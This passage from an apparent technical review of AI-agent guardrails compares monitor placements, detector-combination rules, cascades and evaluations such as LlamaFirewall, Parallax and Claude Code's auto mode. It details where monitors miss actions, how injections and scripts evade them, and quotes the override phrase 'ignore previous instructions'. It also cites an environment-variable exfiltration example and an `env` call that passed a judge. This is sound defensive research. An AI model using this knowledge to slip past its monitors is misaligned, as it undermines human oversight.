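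In a test with 190 simulated runs, ActPlane detected 77% of the violations. Three detectors that worked on tool calls (an LLM filter, text patterns and a data-flow tracker) detected between 34% and 40%. The size of the gap depends on the mix of violations in the test. Two-thirds used a script or another indirect route, and the systems did about equally well on the direct ones. ActPlane wrongly intervened in 18 of the 76 runs that followed the rules, compared with 24 to 28 for the other three. In 17 of ActPlane's 18 cases, the language model had written a rule that was too broad.

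A second test used 361 workplace tasks that required a harmful step. Without protection, the agent behaved unsafely in 106 of them, and ActPlane stopped 78 of these. The rules came from the task descriptions, which often named the files or commands involved, so hidden instructions would be harder to anticipate. ActPlane also fired on 16% of the tasks that the agent had handled safely without it. It missed harmful chat messages, harmful file contents and changes made inside an online service, which its hooks cannot recognise. With 32 rules loaded, replayed agent runs took only 1.9% longer.

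### guardscope: comparing predictions with kernel records

To measure what a control checks in practice, Toyoda and colleagues list 15 paths by which an agent's action can take effect, such as a tool call over HTTP or a job the agent schedules for later. They also define eight placements for a control. The first part of guardscope analyses a control's source code and predicts which paths it can check.

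The second part tests the control with 15 fixed actions. A real harness performs them without a language model, so every run is the same. A separate sensor records what happens in the kernel. An action counts as checked if it passed through the control, bypassed if it took effect without passing through it, and prevented if something outside the policy, such as a network block, stopped it. Before each measurement, the control must refuse an action that its policy forbids. Otherwise, an action could be counted as bypassed when the control simply hadn't finished starting.

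Toyoda and colleagues ran all eight placements with the agent harness Pi. They repeated the basic gateway test with OpenClaw and got the same counts. The controls were the gateway module of Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, the open-source agentgateway, two mechanisms built into Pi, and ActPlane. Seven of the 15 test actions were tool calls, and the other eight were file writes, program starts, direct network connections and access to credentials.

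| Placement | Paths it should check, of 15 | Result with the test actions |
|---|---:|---|
| No control | 0 | Nothing checked |
| Gateway for HTTP tool servers | 1 | HTTP tool calls checked |
| The same, with direct connections blocked | 1 | HTTP tool calls checked, direct connections prevented |
| Gateway for all tool servers, with direct connections blocked | 3 | All tool calls checked, direct connections prevented |
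| Permission checks in the harness | 5 | All tool calls checked |
| Permission checks and a gateway | 5 | All tool calls checked |
| Policy engine in the harness | 5 | All tool calls checked |
| Kernel | 13 | 7 of the 8 other actions checked, no tool calls |

The second column leaves out paths where the answer depends on the system's setup. The 15 actions used only four of the 15 paths, so the predictions for the other eleven are untested. This matters because a product may not check everything its position allows. A control in the kernel could in principle check tool calls, but ActPlane checked none of them because it had no hook for that traffic. It also missed one network message, sent by a method that its hooks don't cover. The kernel row's figure of 13 is therefore an upper limit for controls in that position.

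Claude Code can run a hook before its built-in tools read or edit a file, so a detector in the hook can check those calls. This makes at least one prediction about harnesses doubtful. Toyoda and colleagues predict that detectors placed anywhere outside the kernel will miss five paths, including file operations that a harness's built-in tools carry out directly, and they give Claude Code's file tools as their example.

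Even with these reservations, the trade-off between coverage and detail is clear. A control in the kernel can observe many more routes than a hook in the harness, but it receives paths, addresses and process histories instead of the conversation that explains them. It also records activity from other programs on the same machine. Adding a gateway to the harness's own checks gave the detectors more to read but covered no additional actions. The harness checks covered the seven tool calls and ActPlane covered seven of the other eight actions, so the pair should cover 14 of the 15. Toyoda and colleagues recommend this kind of pairing but didn't test it.

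*AgentKernel* (2026) proposes connecting the two levels more closely. A check of the agent's intent produces a list of system calls that a tool may make, and the kernel enforces the list on every process the tool starts. This would stop a summarising tool that needs only local files from opening a network connection. It would help less with the build-summary script, which needs the network for its legitimate work.

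### When the world changes after the check

A detector in the right place can still approve an action too early. Suppose a user allows an agent to delete an old branch, and a colleague adds new work to it before the deletion runs. The same command would now also delete the colleague's work, which nobody intended. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use problem. *Mind the Gap* (2025) applies the term to agents that read or validate something in one step and rely on it in a later one.

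Zihao Zheng's group, whose database guards appeared earlier, studied the problem with pairs of scenarios, one unsafe and one harmless. The pairs covered sixteen operations, such as restarting a job, deleting a file or granting someone a role. In one pair, another process makes a change just before the agent promotes a validated data snapshot. That process marks the validation as failed in the unsafe version and changes only an audit number in the harmless one.

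Each guard faced 3,520 scripted decisions. In 1,600, a change made the action unsafe. In another 1,600, a change did not make the action unsafe, because it altered only an irrelevant part of the same record (1,280 cases) or some monitoring data (320). In the remaining 320, nothing changed. The researchers chose this mix, so the even split doesn't estimate how often changes are dangerous in real systems. It allows a fair comparison of guards, since a guard that blocks after every change gets half of the changed cases wrong.

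A separate check immediately before the write gave no protection when the change came between the check and the write. All 1,600 dangerous writes went through, as they did with no check. The guards that worked made the condition part of the write, so the database updated the snapshot only if its validation still held. A hook in the harness can't guarantee this alone, because the data is in another system, where other programs can change it.

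In another test, changes arrived at random times. A quick check just before the write failed in at most 0.2% of attempts, because few changes fell in the short gap between the check and the write. Without any check, longer delays made unsafe writes much more common. With one other process making about 20 changes a second, 1.2% of writes were unsafe after a delay of 0.05 seconds and 5.0% after 0.3 seconds. With sixteen such processes and the longer delay, 66% were unsafe. About nine in ten changes in these runs were harmful by design, so the absolute figures are too high for most systems, but the effect of delay should carry over. DeAction's checks took about seven seconds per step, and a person may take hours to approve an action, so the guardrail should check the relevant facts again after a slow verdict.

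Even a condition inside the write may not be enough if it depends on other records. In a further test, an agent could delete a file only if nothing else referred to it. Adding this condition to the delete command stopped every deletion where a reference already existed, but it failed in all 100 trials where another process was still adding the reference when the deletion began. Only a lock solved the problem, because it made the deletion wait until the other process had finished. Both processes had to use the lock, so the guardrail's developer would need control over the other program too.

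### How long an approval lasts

Shraga, Eshel and Gorelik (2026), in *Approved Too Late*, measured how quickly approvals expire in five simulated control systems, such as a sensor network and a service that distributes computing jobs. They rechecked each proposed action, unchanged, eight simulation steps later. Between 3.4% and 24.7% of the initially correct approvals were wrong by then. An LLM judge that takes two seconds causes a delay of eight steps in a system that updates every quarter of a second.

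To limit this, they estimate how long each approval will remain valid:

$$\text{lifetime in steps} = \frac{\text{distance from the safety limit}}{\text{recent change per step}}$$

If a network may lose at most 10% of its messages, now loses 6%, and its loss rate has recently changed by one percentage point per step, an approval stays valid for about four steps. Refusing older approvals reduced the share that had expired to between 0% and 1.8%. Some of that improvement may come from refusing more actions. The researchers tested how these refusals affected performance in only one of the five systems, where performance did not fall.

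The method suits values that usually change gradually, such as a budget or a server's load. It can't predict when a manager will withdraw permission, so a guardrail has to check the permission again when the action runs. Shraga and colleagues recommend that every approval record the action and situation checked, the time of the observation, when the approval expires or needs a new check, and what to do if it has expired.

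### What a claim of coverage must specify

The claim "the guardrail checks every action" is too vague to test. The developer has to name the routes the guardrail covers and the information it reads on each one. Exact versions also matter, since ActPlane loaded on only one of the three kernel versions Toyoda and colleagues tried. Their method also requires an independent record of what the agent did, because a guardrail's own log can't include the actions that bypassed it.

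A claim about a control should also separate coverage from accuracy, because a control can check an action and still make the wrong decision. The claim should also state whether the control acts before or after an operation. ActPlane can refuse some operations before they happen, but it can end a process only after the operation has happened.

For the build-summary agent, a useful claim might be that the hook holds every tool call sent by a named version of the harness, reads the arguments and the user's messages, and repeats its check if the call hasn't run within ten seconds. The developer would also have to say that the hook doesn't check connections a script opens while running.

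## How signals from several detectors are combined

A hook in the harness and a control in the kernel mostly check different actions, so using both mainly adds coverage. When several detectors check the same action, the guardrail needs a rule for combining their outputs into one decision. With the same two detectors, one rule may block almost 10% of harmless actions and another only 0.25%.

### Any alarm or agreement

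The two simplest rules are to block if any detector raises an alarm, or to block only if all of them do. Suppose two detectors have miss rates *m*<sub>1</sub> and *m*<sub>2</sub> and false-positive rates *f*<sub>1</sub> and *f*<sub>2</sub>. If their errors are independent, the combined rates are

$$\text{any alarm:}\quad m = m_1m_2, \qquad f = 1-(1-f_1)(1-f_2)$$

$$\text{agreement:}\quad m = 1-(1-m_1)(1-m_2), \qquad f = f_1f_2$$

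Blocking an action when any detector flags it reduces misses but adds false positives, and requiring detectors to agree does the reverse. The table shows hypothetical detectors that each miss 10% of harmful actions and flag 5% of harmless ones. The last column assumes that one action in a thousand is harmful.

| Rule | Harmful actions missed | Harmless actions blocked | Alarms that are right |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
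| One detector | 10% | 5% | 1.8% |
| Two detectors, any alarm | 1% | 9.75% | 1.0% |
| Two detectors, agreement | 19% | 0.25% | 24% |
| Three detectors, at least two alarms | 2.8% | 0.7% | 12% |

A majority vote of three detectors lowers both error rates, but only because the example assumes their errors are independent. Three detectors that always made the same mistakes would be no better than one.

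### Weighted scores and vetoes

Counting votes treats all detectors as equally reliable. A weighted score gives each detector *i* a weight *w<sub>i</sub>*, which counts only if that detector raises an alarm (*x<sub>i</sub>* = 1, otherwise 0):

$$\text{block if } \sum_i w_i x_i \ge t, \qquad w_i = \ln\frac{(1-m_i)(1-f_i)}{m_i f_i}$$

These weights are the best ones when the detectors' errors are independent. The threshold *t* depends on how common harmful actions are and how serious each kind of error is. The combination follows the any-alarm rule if *t* is low enough for any single alarm to reach it, and requires agreement if only the sum of all the weights reaches it.

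Suppose a written rule misses 40% of harmful actions but flags only 0.1% of harmless ones, while an LLM judge misses 10% and flags 5%. Their weights are 7.3 and 5.1. If one action in a thousand is harmful, the alarms mean the following:

| Alarm from | Probability that the action is harmful |
|---|---:|
| Rule and judge | 92% |
| Rule only | 6% |
| Judge only | 0.7% |
| Neither | 0.004% |

A developer could block the action when both the rule and the judge raise an alarm, ask the user when only the rule does, and log the action when only the judge does. The judge catches more harmful actions than the rule, but its alarm is weaker evidence because it flags so many harmless ones. A developer can also use labelled actions to learn how much weight to give each detector, as ShieldAgent does for its rules. Learned weights can account for errors that the detectors share, but they depend on the mix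 of actions in the training data.

When one detector has an absolute veto, the guardrail blocks any action that detector flags, whatever the other detectors report, so they cannot correct its false positives. A veto therefore suits rules with almost no legitimate exceptions, such as one that stops an agent from editing the guardrail's own settings. Conversely, if an allow list ends the check early, no later detector can catch a harmful action that the list permits.

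### Cascades

Running every detector on every action can be slow, so many guardrails use a cascade. In a common design, a fast first stage checks everything and a slower second stage reviews only what the first stage flags. CodeShield's two tiers and the stages of Claude Code's auto mode work this way.

If the guardrail blocks an action only when the second stage confirms the alarm, the cascade is an agreement rule. Let *m*<sub>2</sub> and *f*<sub>2</sub> now be the second stage's error rates on the actions that reach it. Then

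$$m = m_1 + (1-m_1)\,m_2, \qquad f = f_1f_2$$

The first expression is the agreement formula written differently. The second stage can remove false alarms, but it cannot catch a harmful action that the first stage passed, and it wrongly clears some harmful actions that the first stage flagged.

Suppose a two-stage guardrail checks 100,000 calls, of which 100 are harmful. The first stage misses 10% of the harmful calls and flags 10% of the harmless ones, so it sends 90 harmful and 9,990 harmless calls to a judge. If the judge misses 10% of the harmful calls it receives and flags 5% of the harmless ones, the guardrail blocks 81 harmful calls and about 500 harmless ones. Adding the judge raises the share of flagged calls that are harmful from 0.9% to 14%, but it also raises the number of harmful calls missed from 10 to 19. The judge runs on about a tenth of the calls, so if it takes two seconds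 and the first stage takes 30 milliseconds, the average delay is about 0.23 seconds.

The false-positive rate in this example may be too low. The harmless calls that reach the judge already looked suspicious, so a judge that flags 5% of ordinary harmless calls could flag far more of these. If it flagged 30% of them, it would block about 3,000 harmless calls.

A cascade can also work the other way round, with the first stage blocking the actions it flags and sending the rest to the second. An alarm from either stage then blocks the action. This reduces misses, but the second stage, which uses more compute, has to check nearly every action because most raise no alarm in the first.

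### LlamaFirewall's two scanners

Chennabasappa and colleagues tested the any-alarm rule with two LlamaFirewall detectors that read different parts of a run. AlignmentCheck reads the agent's reasoning and actions. PromptGuard 2 is a small classifier that checks user messages and tool results for explicit attempts to override an agent's instructions, such as "ignore previous instructions".

PromptGuard 2 has a deliberately narrow task. Its predecessor was also meant to detect attacks that change the agent's goal in subtler ways, but it raised too many false alarms because it had no information about what the user wanted. In Meta's private English test, the larger version of PromptGuard 2, with 86 million parameters, caught 97.5% of attacks at a false-positive rate of 1%, compared with 21.2% for its predecessor. It took 92 milliseconds to check 512 tokens on a data-centre graphics processor.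 A smaller version, with 22 million parameters, took 19 milliseconds and caught 88.7% of attacks.

The combined test replayed AgentDojo runs by ten models, with and without prompt injections. If either detector raised an alarm at any point, an attack counted as stopped and a harmless task as failed.

| Guardrail | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---:|---:|
| None | 17.63% | 47.73% |
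| PromptGuard 2 | 7.53% | 47.01% |
| AlignmentCheck | 2.89% | 43.09% |
| Both | 1.75% | 42.68% |

PromptGuard 2 missed 42.7% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded (7.53 divided by 17.63), and AlignmentCheck missed 16.4%. If their misses were independent, both would miss 7.0% of these attacks, and the overall attack success rate would be about 1.2%. The measured rate was 1.75%, so the misses overlap more than independence would predict. AlignmentCheck missed 23% of the attacks that PromptGuard 2 missed, compared with 16.4% of all attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. If the misses had overlapped completely, the rate would have been 2.89%, the same as with AlignmentCheck alone, so the pair is still clearly better.

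The false alarms overlap too. The percentages in the last column match 970 harmless runs, with ten models each attempting AgentDojo's 97 tasks. The agents completed 463 of these runs without a guardrail. Of those 463, PromptGuard 2 flagged 7, AlignmentCheck flagged 45, and together they flagged 49, so both flagged 3 of the same runs. If the false alarms were independent, task completion would have been 42.4% instead of the measured 42.7%, but a difference of two or three runs could easily be due to chance.

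Adding PromptGuard 2 to AlignmentCheck stopped 39% of the remaining attacks and lost four completed tasks in 970, which is a good trade-off for such a small model. AlignmentCheck itself loses much more work. It flagged almost 10% of the completed harmless runs, although its false-positive rate on Meta's benchmark was only 2.5%.

The attack figures probably overstate the protection. An alarm counted as prevention even if it came after the attack had succeeded, and every attack used the same "important instructions" template. Chennabasappa and colleagues acknowledge that PromptGuard 2 may do worse against more varied attacks.

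### Overlapping misses

In *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, Yang (2026) measured how often different kinds of detector miss the same dangerous actions. He tested AgentTrust's written rules and four LLM judges on 1,119 labelled actions, 560 of them dangerous. The rules missed 13.4% of the dangerous actions and one judge missed 10.5%. If their errors were independent, 1.4% of the dangerous actions would have got past both, and 1.3% (7 actions) did. For two judges that each missed 10.5%, independent errors would have let 1.1% past both, but 5.2% (29 actions) got through.

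The correlation *φ* describes this overlap. It is zero when misses are independent and positive when the detectors tend to miss the same actions:

$$P(\text{both miss}) = m_1m_2 + \varphi\sqrt{m_1(1-m_1)\,m_2(1-m_2)}$$

For these two judges, *φ* is about 0.43. The same calculation gives about 0.16 for LlamaFirewall's two scanners.

Yang also converts the joint miss rate into a number of independent detectors. If *g* is the geometric mean of the separate miss rates, then

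$$n = \frac{\ln P(\text{all miss})}{\ln g}$$

The two judges are equivalent to about 1.3 independent detectors, the rules plus the judge to about 2.1, and LlamaFirewall's PromptGuard 2 and AlignmentCheck to about 1.7. The minimum isn't always 1, because detectors with different miss rates give a higher value even when they overlap completely. For the LlamaFirewall pair, the minimum would be about 1.4.

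How accurate a detector was on its own was a poor guide to how much it added. Yang took each possible group of three judges, found the dangerous actions that all three had missed, and counted how many of those an additional detector caught. The table adds up the results for all four groups, so the same action can count more than once. For the rates in the second column, an escalation to a person counts as a miss.

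| Added detector | Missed on its own | Extra catches if escalation counts as a miss | Extra catches if escalation counts as a catch |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| AgentTrust's rules | 13.9% | 86 | 31 |
| The rules with a cloud pack | 11.1% | 86 | 31 |
| A fourth judge | 13.3% | 22 | 21 |
| A list of 50 text patterns | 85.7% | 9 | 2 |

The cloud pack made the rules more accurate but added nothing to the groups of judges, because at least one judge in every group had already caught each additional action the pack caught. The short list of patterns missed most dangerous actions but caught a few that three judges had missed.

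One judge escalated 47 of the 560 dangerous actions to a person, so the way escalations are counted affects how well it appears to perform. The judge is very useful if the person always stops those actions, but they remain unresolved if nobody is available to answer. A team should therefore decide what happens to escalated actions before it compares combinations of detectors.

The result is good evidence for pairing rules with a judge instead of adding more judges, but the rules may be less independent of the judges on new actions. Yang tuned the rules on one of the three datasets and added to them after testing on another. On a further dataset from a third party, where every detector missed most cases, the rules' overlap with the judges was about halfway between none and complete. No attacker tried to defeat the combination. An attacker who knew the rules could write an action that avoids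 them and concentrate on deceiving the judge.

It is also unclear why the judges miss the same actions. Similar training may have given them the same weaknesses, or some actions may be hard for any detector to catch. Yang estimates that difficulty accounts for 32% to 62% of the overlap, depending on the method.

### When a judge and a rule disagree

Asking the same judge twice adds very little. *When Evaluators of AI Agents Disagree* (Im, 2026) ran 2,160 customer-service episodes on τ²-bench and had GPT-4.1 mini judge each one twice. The two verdicts matched 98.2% of the time, but the judge agreed with the benchmark's scoring, which compares the final database with the correct result, in only 56.2% of episodes. Of the 1,007 episodes the benchmark scored as failures, the judge passed 929.

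Im also tested a simple rule that compares whether the task calls for a database change with whether the agent made one. The rule agreed with the judge in 78.2% of episodes and with the benchmark in 76.1%. In a sample of 120 episodes, human reviewers found 11 in which the agent made a change when it should have made none, such as cancelling a booking in violation of the airline's policy. They found 55 episodes correct in every respect.

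| Evaluator | Forbidden changes passed, of 11 | Correct episodes failed, of 55 |
|---|---:|---:|
| GPT-4.1 mini, full transcript | 10 | 1 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 6 | 11 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol with the written policy | 0 | 40 |
| Simple rule | 0 | 2 |

Im did not test a combined decision, but these counts set limits on how one would perform. If the guardrail blocked only when both GPT-5.6 Sol without the policy and the simple rule flagged a problem, it would stop 5 of the 11 forbidden changes and wrongly fail at most 2 of the 55 correct episodes. If either could block on its own, the guardrail would stop all 11 and wrongly fail between 11 and 13. The rule alone would do better than both combinations on these two measures.

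However, the rule relies on the benchmark for the expected answer, and a live guardrail would need someone to specify in advance which requests justify a change. The rule also checks only whether a change happened. Reviewers found 53 episodes in which the agent's decision to make or withhold a change was wrong, and the rule caught 24. In most of the episodes it missed, a change was appropriate but the agent made the wrong one or made it at the wrong time. GPT-5.6 Sol without the policy caught 34 of the 53, so the judge could still help where the rule cannot decide.

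Im's live checks also show how a later stage can fail because it doesn't receive the evidence. Before each database change, a model reviewed a record of the conversation that kept only the first 800 characters of each message. In one episode, the order's status began at character 950 of a tool result, so the reviewer could not confirm it and repeatedly rejected a legitimate change until the guardrail ended the conversation. In the retail setting, 59% of tool results were longer than 800 characters. A cascade therefore has to pass on the evidence for a decision as well as the action.

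### False alarms in larger combinations

Under the any-alarm rule, overlapping misses are undesirable but overlapping false alarms are helpful, because two detectors that block the same harmless action block fewer harmless actions in total than two that block different ones. *How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?* (2026) measured this with seven defences against jailbreaks, prompts that try to make a chatbot ignore its safety training. The defence with the most false refusals refused 39% of harmless prompts. 60% of harmless prompts were refused by at least one of the seven defences, compared with 81% if their errors had been independent.

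The seven defences refused 83% when assembled into one working system. They interacted in ways that cancelled the benefit of overlap. Adding up separately recorded verdicts, as the LlamaFirewall experiment did, can therefore underestimate a live system's false positives. The effect may differ in size for detectors that only read an agent's actions and do not change what the other detectors receive.

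Running only the detectors that apply can limit false alarms. *MAS-Guard* (2026) selects detectors by the type of event, such as a tool call or a tool result, and by fixed conditions that exclude irrelevant or trusted cases. The selected detectors run in parallel and return verdicts in a common format. For the build-summary agent, the detector for injected instructions would scan only the build log, and the detector for data leaks would scan only the Python script.

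### Parallax: a veto, two votes and a judge

Fokou (2026), in *PARALLAX*, describes a guardrail that combines several of these rules. It handles a proposed call in four steps:

1. Compiled code blocks access to certain files, including the guardrail's configuration and its audit log. No later step can override this veto.
2. A written policy blocks the call, allows it or sends it to a particular later step. A call that matches no rule goes to the next step.
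3. A set of 37 text patterns and a trained classifier check the call in parallel, and a confident alarm from either blocks it. If the classifier suspects an injection but is less than 85% confident, an LLM judge reviews the call.
4. The judge sees only the type of action and its contents. It can allow the call, block it or ask a person.

Fokou tested the system by submitting 280 harmful calls and 50 legitimate ones directly, as if an attacker already controlled the agent. The classifier skipped seven types of action by default, including writing files, sending email and making web requests. The system still checked these calls against its patterns, and the judge then reviewed them.

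| Configuration | Harmful calls blocked | Legitimate calls blocked |
|---|---:|---:|
| Classifier skips seven action types | 277 of 280 | 0 of 50 |
| Classifier checks every type | 280 of 280 | 18 of 50 |

The classifier caused 14 of the 18 false alarms. It was trained to detect prompt injections in text, and it misclassified the contents of ordinary files, emails and web requests as attacks. Its confidence was 1.00 each time, so raising the threshold would not have helped. Under the any-alarm rule, this one unsuitable detector made the whole guardrail unusable.

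The judge caused the other four false alarms, all on shell commands. Shell commands follow the same path in both configurations, so Fokou attributes these four to the judge giving different verdicts on different runs. The classifier's effect is therefore closer to 14 in 50 than 18 in 50.

The three harmful calls that got through in the default configuration also reached the judge. One was `env`, which prints the environment variables. The judge classified it as a harmless read. The judge's narrow input protects it from manipulation but can hide the agent's reason for the call, as with Google's Critic.

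Both block rates are probably too favourable. Fokou added rules and 17 patterns after early tests exposed gaps, then reported results for the improved system. With only 50 legitimate calls, even zero false alarms is compatible with a true false-alarm rate of about 6%.

### The cost of each design

*Benchmarking Jailbreak Guardrails for Embodied Agents* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compared six guardrails on the same simulated household robot. It measured each guardrail's own running time on safe tasks, and how often each failed to intervene when a jailbreak asked the robot to do something dangerous.

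| Guardrail | How it decides | Seconds per task | Attacks without intervention |
|---|---|---:|---:|
| AgentSpec | Fixed rules | 0.00 | 80% |
| Llama Guard 3 Vision and EMBGuard, eight variants | Trained classifier | 0.12–0.60 | 33–66% |
| RoboGuard | Rules that an LLM adapts to the scene | 7.59 | 82% |
| MADRA | Several LLMs that debate the request | 9.72 | 22% |
| RoboSafe | An LLM that reasons about every action | 22.81 | 7% |

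RoboSafe interrupted 93% of attacks but also 91% of safe tasks, so its alarms give almost no information about whether a task is dangerous. It looks like the strongest detector only if the safe tasks are left out. Adding it to another detector under the any-alarm rule would stop most legitimate work, and requiring both to agree would hardly reduce the other detector's false alarms. AgentSpec caught few attacks but interrupted only 3.4% of safe tasks, so its alarms were much more informative, and it added almost no delay.

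If detectors run in parallel, the delay is that of the slowest. In a cascade it is

$$t = t_1 + q\,t_2$$

where *q* is the share of actions that the first stage passes on. If a classifier took 0.6 seconds and sent 10% of tasks to MADRA, the average delay would be about 1.6 seconds instead of 9.7. But the classifiers in this benchmark missed at least a third of the attacks, and MADRA would never see those.

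A cascade also saves little time if its early stage is slow. In Parallax, the written policy took less than a millisecond, but the classifier stage took a median of 1.95 seconds, almost as long as the judge's 2.09 seconds. Fokou attributes the delay to how the program loads the classifier and expects a different implementation to take less than 50 milliseconds.

Giving a single detector more evidence can also make it miss more attacks. When the researchers gave Llama Guard the robot's camera image as well as the user's instruction, the share of attacks it missed rose from 40% to 54%, while its false-positive rate fell from 2.7% to 1.7%. They suggest that the image, which mostly showed ordinary household objects, drew attention away from the dangerous instruction.

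### Combining a specification with learned behaviour

A guardrail can also combine two methods inside one detector, which then produces a single signal. Sekar, Gupta and colleagues (2002) did this for network traffic in *Specification-based Anomaly Detection*. They wrote a specification of how a network protocol works, and the detector learned how often each permitted step normally occurs.

The simplest example is a gateway that forwards messages from the internet to machines in an organisation. The specification is a state machine. When a message for an internal machine arrives, the state changes from "start" to "received". It changes to "done" when the gateway forwards the message, or after 60 seconds if the gateway hasn't forwarded it. The second kind of change is called a timeout, and it is permitted because the internal machine may be switched off or its address may be wrong.

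Suppose an attacker sends messages to hundreds of addresses to find out which ones are in use. Many don't exist, so the number of timeouts rises sharply. A specification alone raises no alarm because each timeout is allowed. A conventional anomaly detector could find the attack, but an expert would probably have to configure it to count how many addresses each sender contacts. Sekar and colleagues' detector counts how often each step in the specification's state machine occurs, over periods from a millisecond to 1,000 seconds, and raises an alarm when a count is far above its highest level in training. It can therefore detect the attack without a rule written for it.

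In a 1999 test, the detector found all 43 attacks that the researchers considered within its scope, with an average of 5.5 false alarms a day. They excluded attacks that needed only one abnormal message because the method depends on repetition. They also acknowledged that other researchers had questioned how realistic the test data were.

ProbGuard divides the work similarly for agents. Experts define the states, and the system learns the probabilities. For the build-summary agent, a specification could permit the steps "fetch builds", "retry after an error" and "post summary". The detector would learn how many retries are normal and could flag a run with hundreds, even though each retry is allowed. It would be much less useful against the script that sends the environment variables to `METRICS_HOST`, because a single request can leak them all without noticeably changing any frequency.

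## Two deployed combinations: Claude Code's auto mode and Codex's Auto-review

Auto mode in Claude Code and Auto-review in OpenAI's Codex both use a language model instead of a person to decide whether to approve an agent's actions. Auto mode reviews most commands before they run. Auto-review lets the agent act freely inside a sandbox and reviews only its requests to act outside it.

Claude Code used to ask users before running most commands or changing files. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, users accepted 93% of these requests and over time stopped paying close attention. Anthropic launched auto mode on 24 March 2026 (Willison, 2026, *Auto mode for Claude Code*) and made it the default for individual and team plans in August. The 93% acceptance rate alone doesn't prove that users were careless, since a perfect reviewer would accept 99.9% of requests if one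 in a thousand were dangerous.

### One tool call in auto mode

Suppose the agent writes the build-summary script to `summary.py` in the project folder and then proposes the command `python summary.py`. The checks below follow the order in Anthropic's current documentation, *Permission modes*.

Claude Code first applies the user's permission rules, which are specification-based. A rule can allow calls that match a pattern, forbid them, or require Claude Code to ask the user. Many users have a rule that allows every command starting with `python`, which would let the script run without further checks. Auto mode therefore suspends rules broad enough to permit arbitrary code, but keeps narrow ones such as a rule for `npm test`.

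Claude Code also allows most reads, and edits inside the project folder, without a review, except for certain protected files such as its own settings. This rule is another specification, based on the type of action and the file's location, and it lets the agent create `summary.py`. Anthropic accepts the risk because developers can inspect such edits through version control.

Neither rule covers running the script, so the command goes to the classifier, an LLM judge with two stages. The first stage is a fast filter that answers yes or no with a single token and is instructed to block when in doubt. If it flags the call, the second stage gives the model the same prompt with a different final instruction, and the model reasons about the call before giving the final verdict. Because the prompts are otherwise identical, the second stage can reuse most of the first stage's computation.

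The classifier's prompt combines several kinds of detector. It contains a written policy, with more than twenty default block rules, some exceptions and a description of which repositories and services to trust. The model must also work out what a command or script would really do, as a code detector does, and check whether the user authorised the action, which is an intent comparison.

When the agent tries to run `python summary.py`, the classifier's input includes the earlier call that created the file, with the line that sends the environment variables to `METRICS_HOST`. The default rules forbid sending sensitive data to outside addresses, so the classifier should block the command. The agent would then be told which rule it had broken, and could delete the last line and try again.

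After the corrected script runs, a separate probe scans its output for prompt injections before the agent reads it. The probe is a learned detector, like PromptGuard 2, that checks text instead of actions. If a build log seems to contain planted instructions, the probe adds a warning but doesn't withhold the log. An injection therefore succeeds only if the agent follows it despite any warning and the classifier allows the resulting call. Anthropic gives no separate error rates for the probe.

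An agent can also delegate part of its work to a subagent. The subagent receives its task where the user's message normally appears, so any task would look authorised to the classifier that monitors the subagent. Auto mode therefore checks the task when the agent delegates it, while the classifier still has the user's real request. It checks the subagent's work again at the end, because an injection may have hijacked the subagent, but this check only adds a warning to the subagent's report.

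### What the classifier reads

In the original design, the classifier received only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removed everything else the agent wrote, because an agent can argue for a bad action, for instance by claiming that the user implicitly approved it. It also removed tool results, as AlignmentCheck does, to keep injections out. According to Anthropic, the classifier now also receives `CLAUDE.md`, a file of standing instructions for the agent, and no longer receives calls that only read or search files.

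Anthropic compared the original input with two alternatives. Adding the agent's text and the tool results made the classifier worse at detecting overeager actions, in which the agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user allowed. The company suggests that a shorter transcript is easier to judge and gives the agent less influence over the verdict. Given only the tool calls, the classifier missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things users had plainly asked for.

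The second result is expected from cases like `kubectl get secret`, where only the request separates a harmless command from a theft. The first is less certain because Anthropic gives no figures for the comparison, the set of overeager actions is small, and both kinds of text were added at once, so it's unclear which caused the problem.

The narrow input has a known drawback. If the agent tries to cancel job `abc123` and the user never mentioned that ID, the classifier can't determine whether the agent found it in a list of the user's jobs or made it up.

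### What the reasoning stage adds and removes

Anthropic tested the classifier on 10,000 tool calls from its employees' sessions and on 52 real overeager actions, which an employee had denied or someone had flagged afterwards. It also tested the classifier on 1,000 generated attempts to exfiltrate data, many of them disguised.

| Measure | Fast filter alone | Both stages |
|---|---:|---:|
| Harmless calls flagged, of 10,000 real calls | 8.5% | 0.4% |
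| Dangerous actions missed, of 52 real ones | 6.6% | 17% |
| Dangerous actions missed, of 1,000 synthetic ones | 1.8% | 5.7% |

Auto mode blocks a call only if both stages flag it. The fast filter wrongly flagged about 850 of the 10,000 calls. The reasoning stage cleared about 810 of them and blocked 40, or 4.7% of the harmless calls it received.

It also cleared some dangerous actions. On the synthetic attacks, the filter flagged 982 and the reasoning stage let 39 of those through, about 4%. On the real overeager actions, the share was

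$$\frac{0.17-0.066}{1-0.066} \approx 11\%$$

The 17% is 9 of the 52 actions, so the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. The filter's 6.6% would be 3.4 actions, so it can't be a simple count and may be an average over several runs. The two stages differ by only five or six actions. Anthropic also tuned the filter on this set, which probably makes the 6.6% too low. The set can't include damage that nobody noticed.

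Now suppose that one in every thousand calls reaching the classifier is dangerous. For 100,000 calls, the measured rates would give:

| Result | Fast filter alone | Both stages |
|---|---:|---:|
| Dangerous calls flagged, of 100 | 93 | 83 |
| Harmless calls flagged, of 99,900 | 8,492 | 400 |
| Alarms that are right | 1.1% | 17% |

The reasoning stage thus prevents about 8,100 false alarms but misses ten more dangerous calls. The share of correct alarms would be 15% if auto mode missed 30% of dangerous calls and 19% if it missed 9%. The false-positive rate affects this share more, and it comes from Anthropic's employees, so a company with unusual infrastructure could have a very different one.

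If the errors are independent, a harmless session with 100 reviewed calls has a 33% chance of at least one false block. After a block, the agent normally gets a chance to find another way. If a block ended the session instead, this error rate would be a serious problem.

### Why most misses concerned consent

In the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had usually identified the danger, such as a deletion or a force push (which overwrites the history of a branch on a shared server), but had wrongly classed the action as authorised by the user. In one example, the user had asked the agent to "clean up the PR" (pull request, a proposed change that colleagues review) but had not mentioned a force push. In other cases the user had approved a similar action earlier, and the classifier treated this as permission for the new one.

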